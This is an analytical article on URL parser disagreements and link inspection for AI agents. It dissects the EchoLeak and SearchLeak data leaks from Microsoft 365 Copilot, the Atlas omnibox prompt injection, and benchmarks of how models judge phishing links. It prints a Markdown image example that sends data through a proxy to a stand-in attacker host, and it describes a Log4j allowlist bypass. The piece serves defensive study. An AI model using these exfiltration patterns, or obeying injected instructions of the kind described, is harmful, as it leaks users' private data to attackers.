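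Missing slashes cause a similar disagreement. Under the RFC grammar, `https:example.org` has a scheme and a path but no host, so an inspector might dismiss it as a link within the same site. A browser opening it from an email adds the slashes and goes to example.org. On a page at `https://example.com/`, WHATWG's rules turn the same text into `https://example.com/example.org`, because the page and the link share a scheme. On a page served over plain `http`, it leads to example.org. An inspector that extracts links from a page therefore has to parse them together with the page's address.

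Browsers have changed how they read some addresses. WebKit, the project behind Safari's browser engine, gives the example of a link to `https:/webkit.org`, with only one slash, on a page at example.org. The link used to open webkit.org, but after a change to WebKit's parser it opened `https://example.org/webkit.org`, as in Chrome and Firefox.

Browsers also delete tabs and line breaks anywhere in an address, even in the middle of `https`. An inspector that ends an address at the first whitespace gets only part of the address the browser opens.

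Parsers that follow the same standard can still treat an address differently. caruso (2023), in *URLParser should parse URLs including authority and a backslash after the host*, reported that Safari's parser rejected an address that Chrome, Firefox and the JavaScript platform Node.js accepted. WebKit's developers have since fixed this.

The repairs remain contentious. In January 2026, RelunSec, a commenter on WHATWG's issue tracker, pointed out that browsers turn `http:localhost` into a working address for the user's own machine, so the malformed version can get past filters that expect only the correct form. RelunSec proposed that browsers keep repairing such addresses for compatibility, while other software rejects them. Rejection seems right for an inspector, because real invoices rarely contain links with missing slashes and refusing one does little harm.

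### Tests of parser disagreement

At the Black Hat conference in 2017, Orange Tsai presented flaws of this kind that he had found with a fuzzer, a program that generates large numbers of unusual inputs. They affected built-in libraries in Python, PHP, Perl, Ruby, Java and JavaScript, as well as the download tools Wget and curl. *A New Era of SSRF* (2017) gives the root cause as inconsistency between the code that parses an address and the code that requests it.

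In January 2022, the security companies Claroty and Snyk published a comparison of 16 parsers. Claroty describes five sources of disagreement:

- missing or malformed schemes
- an irregular number of slashes
- backslashes
- percent-encoded data
- parsing an address without the rules specific to its scheme

The two companies also found eight vulnerabilities in web applications and libraries. Developers had patched all of them except those in unsupported versions of the Python framework Flask.

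Claroty's account of Log4j, a Java logging library, shows how a difference between parsers can defeat an allowlist. After a severe flaw was disclosed in December 2021, Log4j's developers restricted certain lookups to permitted hosts, by default only the local machine. Attackers could get around this with a host such as `127.0.0.1#.example.net`. The parser that checked the address ended the host at the number sign, leaving `127.0.0.1`, which was permitted. On some systems, mainly macOS, the code that sent the request used the whole string as the host name, which the holder of example.net controls. The developers fixed the bypass in version 2.16.0.

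Both standards end the authority at a number sign, so the checker, not the fetcher, parsed the address correctly. Giving a checker the more correct parser does not provide protection if the fetcher uses a different one.

Reynolds, Bates and Bailey (2022), in *Equivocal URLs*, measured agreement between widely used parsers and found that every one departed from the standards somewhere. They grouped thousands of differences into seven pitfalls. The number of differences is not a good measure of risk by itself, because a disagreement over the path is usually less serious than one over the host. But some of their addresses made different programs contact different hosts. The team also used such addresses to evade Google Safe Browsing and VirusTotal, two services that identify malicious links. This is the most relevant result for an inspector that relies on an outside reputation service, since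 that service has its own parser.

In a dissertation, Reynolds (2022) describes nine differences across more than a dozen parsers and notes that they can also cause false alarms.

Developers often build agent tools with parsers that Claroty tested, although none of the 16 was built specifically for agents. They include Python's urllib and urllib3, and the parsers in Node.js, curl and Chrome. An assistant that inspects URLs with Python and opens them with a Chrome-based tool would combine two of the tested parsers. Developers have changed some of the code in the several years since the tests, so a team would have to repeat them on its own versions. Leitschuh (2023) started a public list of security problems caused by parser differences, which is a useful source of test cases.

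Knowing which standard a library claims to follow isn't enough to predict exactly how it will parse a URL. Sonar, which makes code-analysis software, sorted common parsers by standard and listed Node.js under WHATWG, but cautioned that implementations of the same standard can still differ slightly.

Daniel Stenberg, who created curl, recommends using the same parser to check an address and to fetch it. In *Don’t mix URL parsers* (2022), he explains that curl's library has let other programs use its parser since 2018, so a program that fetches with curl can also check addresses with curl. He had also fixed a bug, reported by the Claroty and Snyk researchers, in how curl handled percent-encoded host names. Using a single parser works well for an agent's own tool, but it doesn't cover links that the user opens, because the inspector's developers don't control the browser.

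If the inspector can't use the same parser as the fetcher, it can rebuild the address from the parts it has identified. For the backslash example, a WHATWG parser would produce `https://example.com/@example.net/`, which both standards read the same way. The inspector must then pass only the rebuilt address to the user or fetcher, because the original could still be read as a different destination.

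### Redirects and short links

A server can answer a request with a redirect, a reply that names another address, and most fetchers then request that address automatically. Websites use redirects to move pages, count clicks and return people to the right place after they log in. Short links also use redirects, so the address `https://short.example/a1` shows who runs the shortening service but not where the link leads.

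Attackers look for open redirects on reputable domains, which forward visitors to any address given in the link. Websites usually try to prevent this by allowing only destinations on the same site, but that check can fail when two parsers read the same address differently. In one of the Flask extensions that Claroty examined, extra slashes or backslashes at the start of a destination let an outside address pass the check. The attack worked only if the site used a web server other than the usual one or had changed a setting.

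According to TechRadar's *Three high-risk AI vulnerabilities discovered in Claude.ai*, the security company Oasis found an open redirect on Claude's own website. Certain addresses on claude.com sent visitors to arbitrary outside domains without validation. Google Ads checked only the host name of an ad's link, so an attacker could have placed an ad that appeared to lead to claude.com but took people elsewhere. Oasis reported the redirect in March 2026, and Anthropic was still working on a fix when TechRadar's article appeared.

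OpenAI cites redirects as one reason a list of trusted sites is insufficient for agents. An inspector has to check every address in a redirect chain before the fetcher requests it, and parsers can disagree about any of them. In *My URL isn't your URL* (2016), Stenberg described servers whose redirects contained the wrong number of slashes. Some browsers followed them, while curl and many other tools didn't. An inspector based on one of those tools would stop at a redirect that the user's browser followed.

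A page can also forward visitors through an HTML tag or a script. A full browser may leave the page immediately, but a simple fetcher that doesn't run scripts stays on it, so an inspector using such a fetcher would report the first page as the destination.

If an outgoing link's address contains private data, an inspector that follows the chain in advance delivers that data to the server, just as the agent would. The inspector therefore has to examine what the address contains before contacting any server to find out where it leads.

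### Cloaking

The same address can also return different content to different visitors, and RFC 3986 does not guarantee otherwise. The content depends on when the address is accessed and can vary with other aspects of the request.

A server receives the visitor's IP address and usually a header naming the program that sent the request. Some ordinary sites use this header to give different browsers different links, as WebKit's developers discuss. In cloaking, an attacker uses the same information to show a harmless page to a security scanner and a hostile one to the intended victim. If an agent's requests have a recognisable header or come from a known range of IP addresses, the server can show the hostile page only to the agent, so a person who opens the link to investigate sees nothing wrong.

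An attacker can get a similar result by making a page malicious only after the mail system has scanned the message. When the assistant opens the link the next morning, the address hasn't changed, so a stored verdict from the scan still appears to apply.

The holder of a domain also controls which IP address its name leads to. The holder's name server can give the inspector a public address and, seconds later, give the fetcher the address of a machine inside the company's network. To prevent this, the fetcher has to connect to the IP address that the inspector approved, without looking up the name again.

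Even a recent visit by the inspector is weak evidence of what content the agent will receive from a page. The inspector can instead examine the response that the agent's fetcher received, before the text reaches the model. This helps against hostile instructions in the page, but it comes too late to stop a leak through the address, which has already been sent with the request.

### When a failed address becomes a command

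Software can make the opposite mistake and treat something that looks like an address as an instruction. ChatGPT Atlas, a browser that OpenAI released in October 2025, has a single bar for both web addresses and requests to the agent, so it has to classify each entry as one or the other.

*OpenAI Atlas Omnibox Prompt Injection* (Jordà, 2025) describes a flaw in that decision. An attacker writes a string that begins like a web address but contains a deliberate error, followed by instructions for the agent. The user copies it, perhaps by pressing a "Copy link" button on a website, and pastes it into the bar. Atlas fails to parse it as an address and passes the whole text to the agent as the user's own request. The agent therefore trusts the attacker's instructions more than it would trust the same text on a web page.

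WHATWG's standard explicitly leaves open how a browser should interpret what people type into the address bar, so each browser maker has to design this step itself.

In the published demonstration, the agent only opened the website of NeuralTrust, Jordà's company, as the hidden text instructed. More serious outcomes, such as deleting files from the user's Google Drive, were hypothetical. The attack also depends on the user pasting the string without reading it, but people rarely read long links closely. NeuralTrust confirmed and published the flaw on 24 October 2025 and reported no fix in its post. In December, OpenAI said that some attacks of this general type on AI browsers were likely to persist, as Nolan (2025) reported in Fortune.

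This route is easier to close than prompt injection in general. Jordà recommends that a browser refuse a malformed address instead of silently treating it as a request, and that users choose explicitly between opening a page and asking the agent. The same caution applies to an agent's tools. A tool that accepts either an address or a search query could send a malformed address, along with any private data it contains, to a search engine without the link inspector checking it.

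## How did reference-style links get past Microsoft 365 Copilot's filter?

Microsoft 365 Copilot's filter removed links to outside websites from its answers, but it recognised only inline links. When the model wrote a reference-style link, with the address in a separate definition, the filter left it in and the user saw a working link. Aim Labs, Aim Security's research group, combined this gap with several others in an attack it called EchoLeak. A single email from outside an organisation could make Copilot send internal data to the attacker's server. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) is the account from the team that found the attack. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) is a case study based only on published material.

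### Timeline and severity

Aim's researchers spent about three months reverse-engineering Copilot. They discovered the flaw in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft, according to Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*. Microsoft attempted a fix in April but found further problems in May. Aim's chief technology officer, Adir Gruss, said the process took five months in all, which he called very long for a flaw of this kind. He attributed the delay partly to the flaw's novelty, because it took time to find the right teams at Microsoft and explain the problem to them. Microsoft made the fixes on its servers in May, according to Field Effect's *Weekly threat roundup* (2025). Microsoft and Aim disclosed the flaw publicly on 11 June.

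GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), a copy of the official vulnerability record with later additions, lists severity scores of 9.3 out of 10 from Microsoft and 7.5 from the US National Vulnerability Database. Both ratings reflect that an attacker needed no account and no action by the user. The scores differ mainly because Microsoft judged that the harm extended beyond the vulnerable component. That seems right, because the flaw in the assistant exposed mail and files held by other services.

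Nobody has reported an attack on a real customer. Microsoft said in its disclosure that no exploitation had occurred, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA also recorded none. This assurance depends largely on Microsoft, which runs the service and holds its logs. Reddy and Gujral point out that a victim would have seen at most what looked like a broken image, so customers would have had little to report.

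### How the email reached the model

Before answering a question, Copilot searches the user's mailbox, files and Teams chats for relevant passages and adds them to the model's input, a method called retrieval-augmented generation. An outsider can't query an organisation's Copilot but can email an employee, and the search may later select that email.

EchoLeak, which is called a zero-click attack, worked only if the user asked Copilot a question for which the search retrieved the attacker's email. The user didn't have to open the email or know that it existed. The researchers made retrieval likely by writing one long email that covered many common workplace topics, such as staff leave, so that the search would find a matching passage for many different questions.

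Microsoft used a classifier to check incoming text for injected instructions, assuming they would look different from ordinary mail. The researchers evaded it by writing the instructions as if to a human recipient. The model then followed them and put sensitive data from its input into a URL at the attacker's domain.

### What the link filter missed

The next control was the filter on Copilot's answers. It allowed links to approved internal pages and removed external ones, but it was designed for links whose destination directly follows the visible text. Ravia found that full, collapsed and shortcut reference links all passed through, and the chat page made them clickable.

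The condition for sound inspection failed because the address was in $F$, the set of addresses that the renderer would use, but not in $I$, the set that the filter extracted. The filter therefore never checked whether the address was internal. Microsoft ran both the filter and the chat page, so it could have based the filter on the renderer's parse tree.

At this stage the attack still needed the user to click a link. The researchers then had the model write an image instead. As with links, the filter caught inline images but missed reference-style ones. The browser loads these images automatically, so the leak no longer required a click.

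### The image policy and the Teams proxy

The browser still refused to load an image from the attacker's domain because Copilot's page had a content security policy (CSP). A CSP is sent with a web page and lists the domains from which the browser may load images and other resources. Unlike the filter, the CSP applies regardless of which Markdown notation produced the image, because the browser checks the actual request.

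The policy's weakness was its list of permitted image sources. The copy Ravia published has 29 distinct entries, 11 of which start with a wildcard that admits every subdomain. The policy was secure only if data sent to a listed domain stayed with the service there. A service that fetches addresses on request can send the data to another server.

The researchers found one such service in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for internal websites, but it worked only if the victim accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Microsoft Teams had another that required no invitation. With reserved domains in place of the real ones, the model's output had this structure:

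```
![chart][c]

[c]: https://preview.example.com/fetch?url=https://example.net/Leeds
```

The browser contacts `preview.example.com`, which the policy permits. That server then requests the address in the `url` parameter, and the owner of `example.net` finds "Leeds" in the log.

Willison calls the Teams address an open redirect, while Ravia says the server makes a request on the browser's behalf. Which account is right affects the repair. A browser also applies the page's CSP to the destination of a redirect, so it would have blocked a redirect to an unlisted domain. It can't control a request that Microsoft's server makes, so Ravia's explanation fits the result better.

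Microsoft had received a warning about a closely related Teams service four years earlier. Positive Security's *MS Teams* (2021) reported that the service behind Teams link previews would fetch any address, including internal ones. Microsoft closed the report in March 2021 without a fix, and the researchers found the same behaviour when they retested it in December. The address they tested and the one in EchoLeak have the same path except for the last part, which is `info` in one and `content` in the other. The two addresses probably belong to the same system, though neither team says so.

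Teams fetched preview images through its own servers to hide the recipient's IP address from the website. In 2021, the main concern about this service was that outsiders could use it to probe Microsoft's internal network. The service became much more dangerous once a language model could write private data into an address for it to fetch.

Copilot normally names the sources of an answer, a last safeguard that could have alerted the user afterwards. But it relied on the model to name them, and the researchers' email got the model to leave that email out.

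### Which repair would have broken the chain?

EchoLeak worked only if every step succeeded, so blocking any one of them would have stopped the published attack. A more demanding test of a fix is whether an attacker could get around it by changing one detail.

| Repair | Link that needs a click | Image through Teams | What an attacker could try next |
|---|---|---|---|
| Train a better injection classifier | stopped for this email | stopped for this email | different phrasing |
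| Make the filter recognise reference-style links | stopped | depends on whether the filter allows the Teams address | another notation |
| Close the Teams proxy | still works | stopped | another permitted service that fetches addresses |
| Load no images from addresses the model wrote | still works | stopped | a link that the user clicks |
| Keep outside email away from internal data | stopped | stopped | outside text that counts as internal |

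Teaching the filter to recognize reference-style links might not have stopped the image, because the filter permitted internal destinations and the Teams proxy was on a Microsoft domain. Ravia doesn't report whether the filter would have removed an inline image with that address. If it treated the address as internal, the attacker didn't need reference-style notation for the image. A repaired filter would need to recognize every link and exclude such proxies from its list of permitted destinations.

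Separating outside email from internal data is the only fix in the table that stops both versions, because the attacker's instructions never share a prompt with internal data. It addresses what Ravia calls an LLM scope violation, in which untrusted text makes a model use trusted data without the user's consent. Willison sees no need for the new term, since prompt injection has always resulted from joining text from different sources. Gruss also blames the mixing of trusted and untrusted data, and he expects a lasting solution to require redesigning either the models or the applications around them.

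The separation makes the assistant less useful because it can't combine a supplier's email with the internal project file, and many people use Copilot for this kind of task. The separation also depends on labelling text correctly. If a colleague forwards the supplier's email, a system that checks only the sender will treat the attacker's text as internal.

Some customers may already have had this option, since Aim Security's *EchoLeak* mentions that organisations can configure Copilot to ignore external email. But Ravia, writing for the same company, states that no administrator's setting could have prevented the attack, as far as the team knew. These claims can hardly both be right if the setting works as described. At best, customers had a protection that was off by default and that few would have known they needed.

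### The mitigations in the case study

Reddy and Gujral propose eight kinds of defence and rate them against the steps of the attack. They call the ratings theoretical in one place and results of "our tests" in another, but they say in their limitations section that they ran no experiments. The ratings therefore rest on arguments, some stronger than others.

They suggest separating sources by trust, using internal sources by default and outside ones only when the user explicitly asks for them. This is the strongest proposal, for the reasons above. They write that EchoLeak "fails by design" if Copilot never uses mail from unknown senders to answer questions about internal projects, but their table marks the same measure as a failure against zero-click leaks. The text is more convincing, because an email that the model never receives can't make it write an image.

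They also recommend putting outside text between tags and telling the model not to follow instructions inside them. Like Microsoft's own marking of outside text, this only makes an injection less likely to succeed, so it is weaker than keeping the text out.

Reddy and Gujral report that Microsoft began removing reference-style links and embedded images from external content. They propose going further and removing all untrusted addresses before the text reaches the model. That would make an attack harder, but the model's answer would still need to be inspected, because in EchoLeak the model wrote the dangerous link itself.

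They recommend limiting the answer to a restricted form of Markdown and a list of permitted domains. A restricted syntax can stop the attack if it excludes images, or if the renderer accepts only what the filter has parsed. The domain list is less reliable than their ratings suggest. They expect it to stop the proxy step, but Copilot had such a list and the Teams proxy was on it. Their advice to avoid wildcards would help more, because someone would have had to add the proxy by name and might have asked what it did.

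A more interesting idea is a signed media proxy, where the application loads images only through its own server and only if the address has a valid, unexpired signature. The server refuses any address the model invents, whatever notation the model used, because that address has no signature. This works only if the application signs just the images it has chosen itself. If it automatically signs every image address in an answer, the server will fetch an attacker's address, as the Teams proxy did.

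Asking the user before contacting an outside site has a similar weakness. Reddy and Gujral imagine a question that names the attacker's domain, and most people would refuse that request. But when the request goes through the proxy, a simple version of the question would name Microsoft Teams. Filters for personal data and unusually random text are also of limited use, because a city name or a six-digit code in a web address is short and looks ordinary.

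### SearchLeak and the rendering race

Another attack was possible a year later because Microsoft had closed one proxy but left the rest of the arrangement in place. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), published on 15 June, describes a chain of flaws in Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches an organisation's mail, meetings and files. Microsoft had listed the chain as CVE-2026-42824 in its 4 June advisory, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026).

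Microsoft has fixed the flaw on its servers and knows of no malicious use, according to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, but its numerical score was 6.5 because the attack needed one click.

That click opened a link to a genuine Microsoft domain. The address contained a search query, and Copilot followed any instructions in the query as soon as the page opened. An attacker could therefore put instructions in the link itself, without planting them in a document or email for Copilot to find. An inspector that checked only the host would have approved the link, and a user who hovered over it would have seen a real Microsoft address.

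The instructions made Copilot search the user's mail and put an email's subject line in the address of an image. Subject lines can contain login codes that stay valid for several minutes. The CSP again blocked unknown domains but allowed Bing, whose image search fetches a picture from any address it receives. Bing's server therefore delivered the data to the attacker. The wildcard entry for Bing was already on the list that Ravia published in 2025, and it still gave attackers a route after the Teams proxy was closed.

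SearchLeak used an HTML image tag instead of a reference-style image. Microsoft had a suitable defence against HTML, which was to place the model's output in a code block so that the browser would show tags as text. But it applied this defence too late:

1. The model wrote the image tag, and the page displayed it while the rest of the answer was still arriving.
2. The browser requested the image from Bing.
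3. The model finished its answer.
4. Copilot put the output in a code block, and the image disappeared.

Varonis calls this a race condition, a flaw in which the result depends on which of two events happens first. The cleaning began only after the answer was complete, so an image near the start was likely to load first, while the model was still writing the rest.

A check on finished text can therefore find every link, parse every address correctly and still fail to prevent a leak. Sound inspection has a further condition when an application streams its answers. For every address $u$ in $F$, the check must finish before the request starts:

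$$t_{\text{check}}(u) < t_{\text{request}}(u).$$

The renderer can satisfy this condition by streaming the words and holding back anything that can cause a request. It can show HTML tags as plain text from the first character and put an inactive placeholder wherever an image would go. It activates an image or link only after the inspector has approved its final address. This is better than waiting for the complete answer before showing any of it, which would also satisfy the condition but would lose the benefit of streaming.

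Varonis also advises developers to sanitize output when it is displayed. It suggests that security teams look for suspicious search links and check whether any permitted domains host services that fetch URLs. That check would have found both the Teams and the Bing proxies. Searching links for HTML tags is less reliable, because an attacker can describe an image in ordinary words and let the model write the tag.

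The timing flaw is also easy to miss in testing. In SearchLeak, the final answer showed a harmless code block, so a tester who read only the saved conversation would have concluded that the defence worked. To catch the flaw, a test has to record the browser's network requests from the moment the first piece of the answer appears.

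## Do language models notice a disguised address?

An inspector with the right parser can tell that a link leads to `example.net`, but something still has to decide whether the agent should visit it. Many agents leave that decision to the language model, which reads the address as text along with the rest of its input. Recent models recognise most scam sites when asked directly, yet agents built on the same models still pay or log in at some of those sites during a task. Older tests, which asked models only to judge an address, gave much worse results, partly because of their design.

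### Eleven manipulations in a multi-agent test

Kong, Peng and colleagues (2025), in *Web Fraud Attacks Against LLM-Driven Multi-Agent Systems*, tested whether one compromised agent could get a malicious link past the others. In the simplest set-up, a travel assistant controlled by the attacker recommends a link, and a second agent, the auditor, rates the link's risk. The team tried eleven kinds of address, ten times each. The table shows how often the attack succeeded against an auditor with no added defence, when the agents ran on GPT-4o-mini in AutoGen, a platform for building multi-agent systems. The examples here use reserved names, and `bank.example` is the site being imitated.

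| Manipulation | Example | Success |
|---|---|---|
| Numeric address | `https://192.0.2.1/` | 40% |
| Attacker's own domain, undisguised | `https://example.net/` | 80% |
| Inserted letter | `https://bankk.example/` | 90% |
| Substituted letter | `https://benk.example/` | 80% |
| Repeated name | `https://bankbank.example/` | 90% |
| Look-alike character | `https://bаnk.example/`, with a Cyrillic а | 40% |
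| Reassuring phrase in the subdomain | `https://official-booking-page.example.net/` | 50% |
| Reassuring phrase in the query | `https://example.net/?official-booking-page` | 60% |
| Reassuring phrase in the path | `https://example.net/official/booking/page` | 20% |
| Known name in the subdomain | `https://bank.example.example.net/` | 0% |
| Known name in the path | `https://example.net/bank/example/` | 10% |

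The undisguised address succeeded in eight of ten runs, and no disguise beat it by more than one run. Putting a known site's name in the subdomain, which works on people because they read the familiar name first, never succeeded here or on the other two platforms, CAMEL and MetaGPT, under the same conditions. GPT-4o-mini mostly accepted an unfamiliar link because another agent recommended it, and several of the disguises revealed the attack. Accepting the plain address is hardly a reading error, since nothing in an unfamiliar domain name shows that its holder is malicious.

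Ten runs per address is a small sample. On MetaGPT, repeating the same address often added little information, because most results were either 0% or 100%, meaning all ten runs gave the same answer.

The team also compared four ways of organising the agents, using GPT-4o-mini on MetaGPT. Averaged over all defence conditions, the attacks succeeded 83.0% of the time in the chain of assistant and auditor. Adding a travel expert who commented on the recommendation raised this to 93.6%. When the assistant debated with an agent that offered a safe link, and an expert chose between the two, the rate was 59.1%. With a vote among three experts, it was 78.2%. An expert choosing at random in the debate would stop half the attacks, so the lower rate there does not necessarily mean that the expert recognised them.

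The scoring also favours the attacker. An attack fails only if the agents choose another link or the auditor answers "high risk", so a medium-risk verdict counts as a success, even though many products would warn the user at that point. The success rate also varied widely by model. In the set-up with the commenting expert, it was about 94% for GPT-4o-mini, 51% for DeepSeek-Reasoner and 27% for Qwen-Plus.

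Kong and colleagues tested three defences borrowed from research on other attacks. On AutoGen, one of them lowered the attack's average success rate from 50.9% to 47.2%, and the other two raised it above 80%. In a separate comparison, deleting one security-related word from the sentence that recommended the link raised the success rate from 0% to 100%, though the address stayed the same. This sensitivity to wording makes the model a poor inspector of links, because the attacker often writes the sentence as well as the link.

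### How MalURLBench scores a model

Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) built a much larger collection of 61,845 disguised addresses in *MalURLBench*. They used real malicious sites in seven categories, including phishing, fraud and malware, and wrote ten everyday scenarios, such as tracking a parcel or looking for a job. Each scenario has 15 templates that add text to the subdomain, path or query around a malicious domain. Each of the 12 models tested judged 3,150 of these addresses, 315 per scenario, five times each.

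A model's risk score for a scenario is the share of addresses it accepts, and its overall score is the unweighted average of its ten scenario scores. Overall scores range from 32.9% for GPT-3.5-Turbo to 99.9%. The 99.9% must belong to Mixtral 8x7B, because that model's score rounds to 1.00 in every scenario.

The lower end of that range depends on a step between the first test and the final result. If a model accepted 10% or fewer of the addresses in a scenario, the team treated the templates as inadequate and had another model, DeepSeek-Coder, work out why they failed and rewrite them. This continued for up to ten rounds. Six of the 12 models resisted well enough to face rewritten templates. Averaging the published scenario scores gives their results before and after:

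| Model | Original templates | After rewriting |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5-Turbo | 14.1% | 32.9% |
| Llama-3-70B | 23.1% | 35.7% |
| Qwen-Plus | 30.0% | 35.7% |
| DeepSeek-Coder | 34.0% | 41.7% |
| GPT-4o | 34.5% | 38.2% |
| Llama-3-8B | 47.0% | 50.6% |

Rewriting is a reasonable imitation of an attacker who can query the target model repeatedly. But it replaces the templates that would produce low scores, so a model can hardly get one. Even the "lowest" score, 32.9%, is more than twice what GPT-3.5-Turbo scored on the templates used on every model. The left-hand column is fairer for comparing models.

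The prompts also help the attacker. Nearly every scenario includes a message that recommends the link, often calling it official or trusted, and the model has to weigh the address against that endorsement. The system prompt does instruct the model to assess risk, but with an odd combination of a personality model and an interrogation technique from criminal psychology. The model must choose one of three risk levels, but its response is scored only as acceptance or refusal, and the paper doesn't state which of these a medium rating counts as.

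The main test measured success by the model's stated judgement, and no agent opened a link. Kong and colleagues also had Browser Use, an agent that controls a browser, visit three of the malicious sites, and all three visits worked. These visits show that a disguised address still works as an address, which the rules of URL syntax already imply.

It is unclear how much disguising an address helps it succeed. In a small trial with Llama-3-8B, two addresses with unmanipulated structures succeeded in 15% and 20% of runs, and two manipulated ones in 60% and 75%. In the travel-assistant test, by contrast, the plain address succeeded more often than most of the disguised ones. The two trials used different models and prompts, and each covered only a few addresses, so neither supports a general figure.

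### Reassuring phrases, known names and domain endings

Across the benchmark, addresses with a reassuring phrase had an average risk score of 71.5%, against 60.89% for addresses that imitated a known site. Kong and colleagues suspect that training data includes the addresses of well-known sites, so models can detect a familiar name in the wrong place. A reassuring phrase has no correct version to compare it with. It also repeats the scenario message's claim about the link, which may further raise the risk score.

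Language models accepted subdomains of up to about 20 characters more often than longer ones, but beyond that point length made no consistent difference. The length of the path or query had no effect. According to the team, this is because ordinary addresses often have long paths and queries but rarely have long subdomains.

The findings on top-level domains, the last part of a host name, are weaker. Models accepted addresses under `.link`, `.art` and `.dev` more often than those under `.com` or `.net`. The paper attributes this to the rarity of the newer endings in training data, but then makes the conflicting argument that models treat the older endings as normal and that attackers could use them to increase their success. The test also used only 21 malicious sites, three from each category, so each ending can have appeared on only a few of them, and the effect of one unusual domain name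 could easily be mistaken for an effect of its ending.

The same caution applies to the claim that larger models accept fewer malicious addresses. The claim is based on six models from three developers, and the models differ in much more than size.

Most of the 12 models are old by the standards of late 2026. GPT-3.5-Turbo dates from March 2023, and the DeepSeek-Chat version in the test is from September 2025. No one appears to have published MalURLBench results for models released in 2026, so its percentages are not estimates for current agents. They remain relevant to products that still use a small or old model for routine checks.

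### URLGuard and the missing false alarms

The same paper proposes URLGuard, a separate model that examines an address before the agent may open it. The team deliberately chose a weak base model, Llama-2-7B, and fine-tuned it on 280 addresses, half malicious and half harmless, each with a label and a written reason for it. The malicious examples came from the shopping scenario, and the test covered the other nine scenarios.

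The average risk score in those nine scenarios fell from about 98% to 17%, and the score fell to zero in four of them. But it was still 61% for music recommendations and 70% for weather information, so URLGuard let through most of the malicious addresses in both. The team attributes this to the small training set.

Kong and colleagues report no results for URLGuard on harmless addresses. This is a serious gap, because a program that refused every address would score a perfect zero on their measure. The harmless half of the training data should discourage URLGuard from refusing everything, but only a test can show whether it did. The malicious test addresses were also built in the same way as those in the training set. URLGuard may therefore have learned to recognise sentences written into addresses, which is useful, without getting better at judging an ordinary-looking domain.

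### Detection and false alarms measured together

Litvak (2026), in *The System Prompt Is the Attack Surface*, tested both kinds of error. Eleven models had to decide whether to follow the links in 1,000 phishing emails and 1,000 harmless ones. A language model wrote the emails, but the phishing links came from public lists of real attacks. Each model worked under ten different system prompts. These are the averages for four of the models under the six general-purpose prompts:

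| Model | Phishing emails blocked | Harmless emails blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 96.9% | 70.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 94.7% | 51.7% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 61.5% | 11.1% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 32.8% | 15.1% |

Claude Sonnet 4.5 would rank first on a benchmark that contained only malicious links, but it also blocked most of the harmless mail, which would make it impractical as an assistant.

The system prompt changed the results as much as the choice of model did. GPT-4o-mini let through less than 1% of the phishing emails when the prompt put security first, and 97% when it put efficiency first. A company could lose the benefit of a more cautious model by adding a sentence about avoiding delays to its mail assistant's prompt. Context also affected the results. When Litvak showed the models only the addresses, without the emails, they found signs of phishing in harmless links, with a false-alarm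 rate of 33%.

The most successful prompts instructed the model to compare the sender's domain with the domain in the link. With one of them, GPT-4o-mini blocked 93.7% of the phishing emails and only 3.8% of the harmless ones. But the two domains matched in 98.4% of the harmless emails, far more often than in real mail, where colleagues often share documents and meeting links from other services. On 100 additional harmless emails in which the two domains differed, GPT-4o-mini blocked 72% and Grok 4.1 Fast blocked 89%.

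An attacker can also make the domains match by registering one domain and using it for both the sender and the link. The collection contained 73 such emails. With the simplest version of the prompt, models detected an average of 43.1% of these emails, compared with 84.6% of the other phishing emails. Litvak examined 281 longer answers in which models had approved such an email, and in 98% of them the models gave the matching domains as a reason. The models had followed their instructions correctly. However, a prompt like this uses a language model to compare domains, which is the part of the job that least needs one because ordinary code can do it exactly.

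A revised prompt let the model block an email with matching domains if something else looked wrong. This correction was useful for GPT-4o-mini, which then caught 76.7% of the difficult emails and blocked 8.2% of harmless mail. With the same prompt, Claude Haiku 4.5 caught 95.9% but blocked 67.6% of harmless mail, which made it unusable.

Litvak then reran ten emails that had got past three models under the revised prompt. Most got through again, as expected, since he had chosen emails that had already succeeded. In its reasons, GPT-4o-mini described an attacker-registered domain as established, although the only evidence it had was the name. Rewording the prompt cannot give a model the domain's registration date or record of past abuse. Litvak recommends giving the model access to such data. The lack of it is also a reason to run a model-based checker after exact checks, not in place of them.

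### What agents do with the link

A model's verdict on a link is only a proxy for what an agent does with it. In *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks*, Li, Zhou and colleagues (2025) at Columbia University and the University of Maryland gave agents real websites to visit. They set up a site for an invented refrigerator with a form that asked for credit card details. Anthropic's Computer Use, an agent that operates a desktop computer, entered the card details in all ten trials when it reached the site through a Reddit post, but in none when the researchers gave it the link directly.

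The team attributes the difference to agents' trust in established platforms. Trust may be part of the cause, but the post also contained instructions for the agent, and the direct link did not. Testing a post with an ordinary link and no instructions would have separated the two causes. Either way, the same address led to opposite outcomes, so the agent's behaviour depended on how the link reached it.

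In another trial, the agent downloaded and ran a file from a site that Li and colleagues had designed to look suspicious, again in all ten attempts after landing on the planted post. The study is small and used an early agent. The researchers had planned to measure a second product, MultiOn, in the same way, but it went offline before they began counting.

Guardio's *Scamlexity* describes tests from 2025 in three scenarios, two of which contained no such instructions. The researchers built a fake Walmart shop, used a real phishing site that imitated the bank Wells Fargo, and hid instructions in a fake captcha. They mainly tested Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, according to iTnews' *AI browsers fall for scams and phishing, security researchers say*.

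Comet put an Apple Watch in the fake shop's cart, filled in the user's address and card details, and bought it. According to Tom's Guide's *AI browsers can’t tell legitimate websites from malicious ones*, Comet sometimes refused or asked the user to finish the purchase, but in most cases it completed the order. It also followed the link in a fake email from a bank manager to a page that asked for login details. "Most cases" is hard to compare with the rates in other studies, and Guardio sells a browser extension that detects scams, as Engadget's *AI browsers may be the best thing that ever happened to scammers* notes. The tests are still good evidence that the failure happens in a commercial product on a live website.

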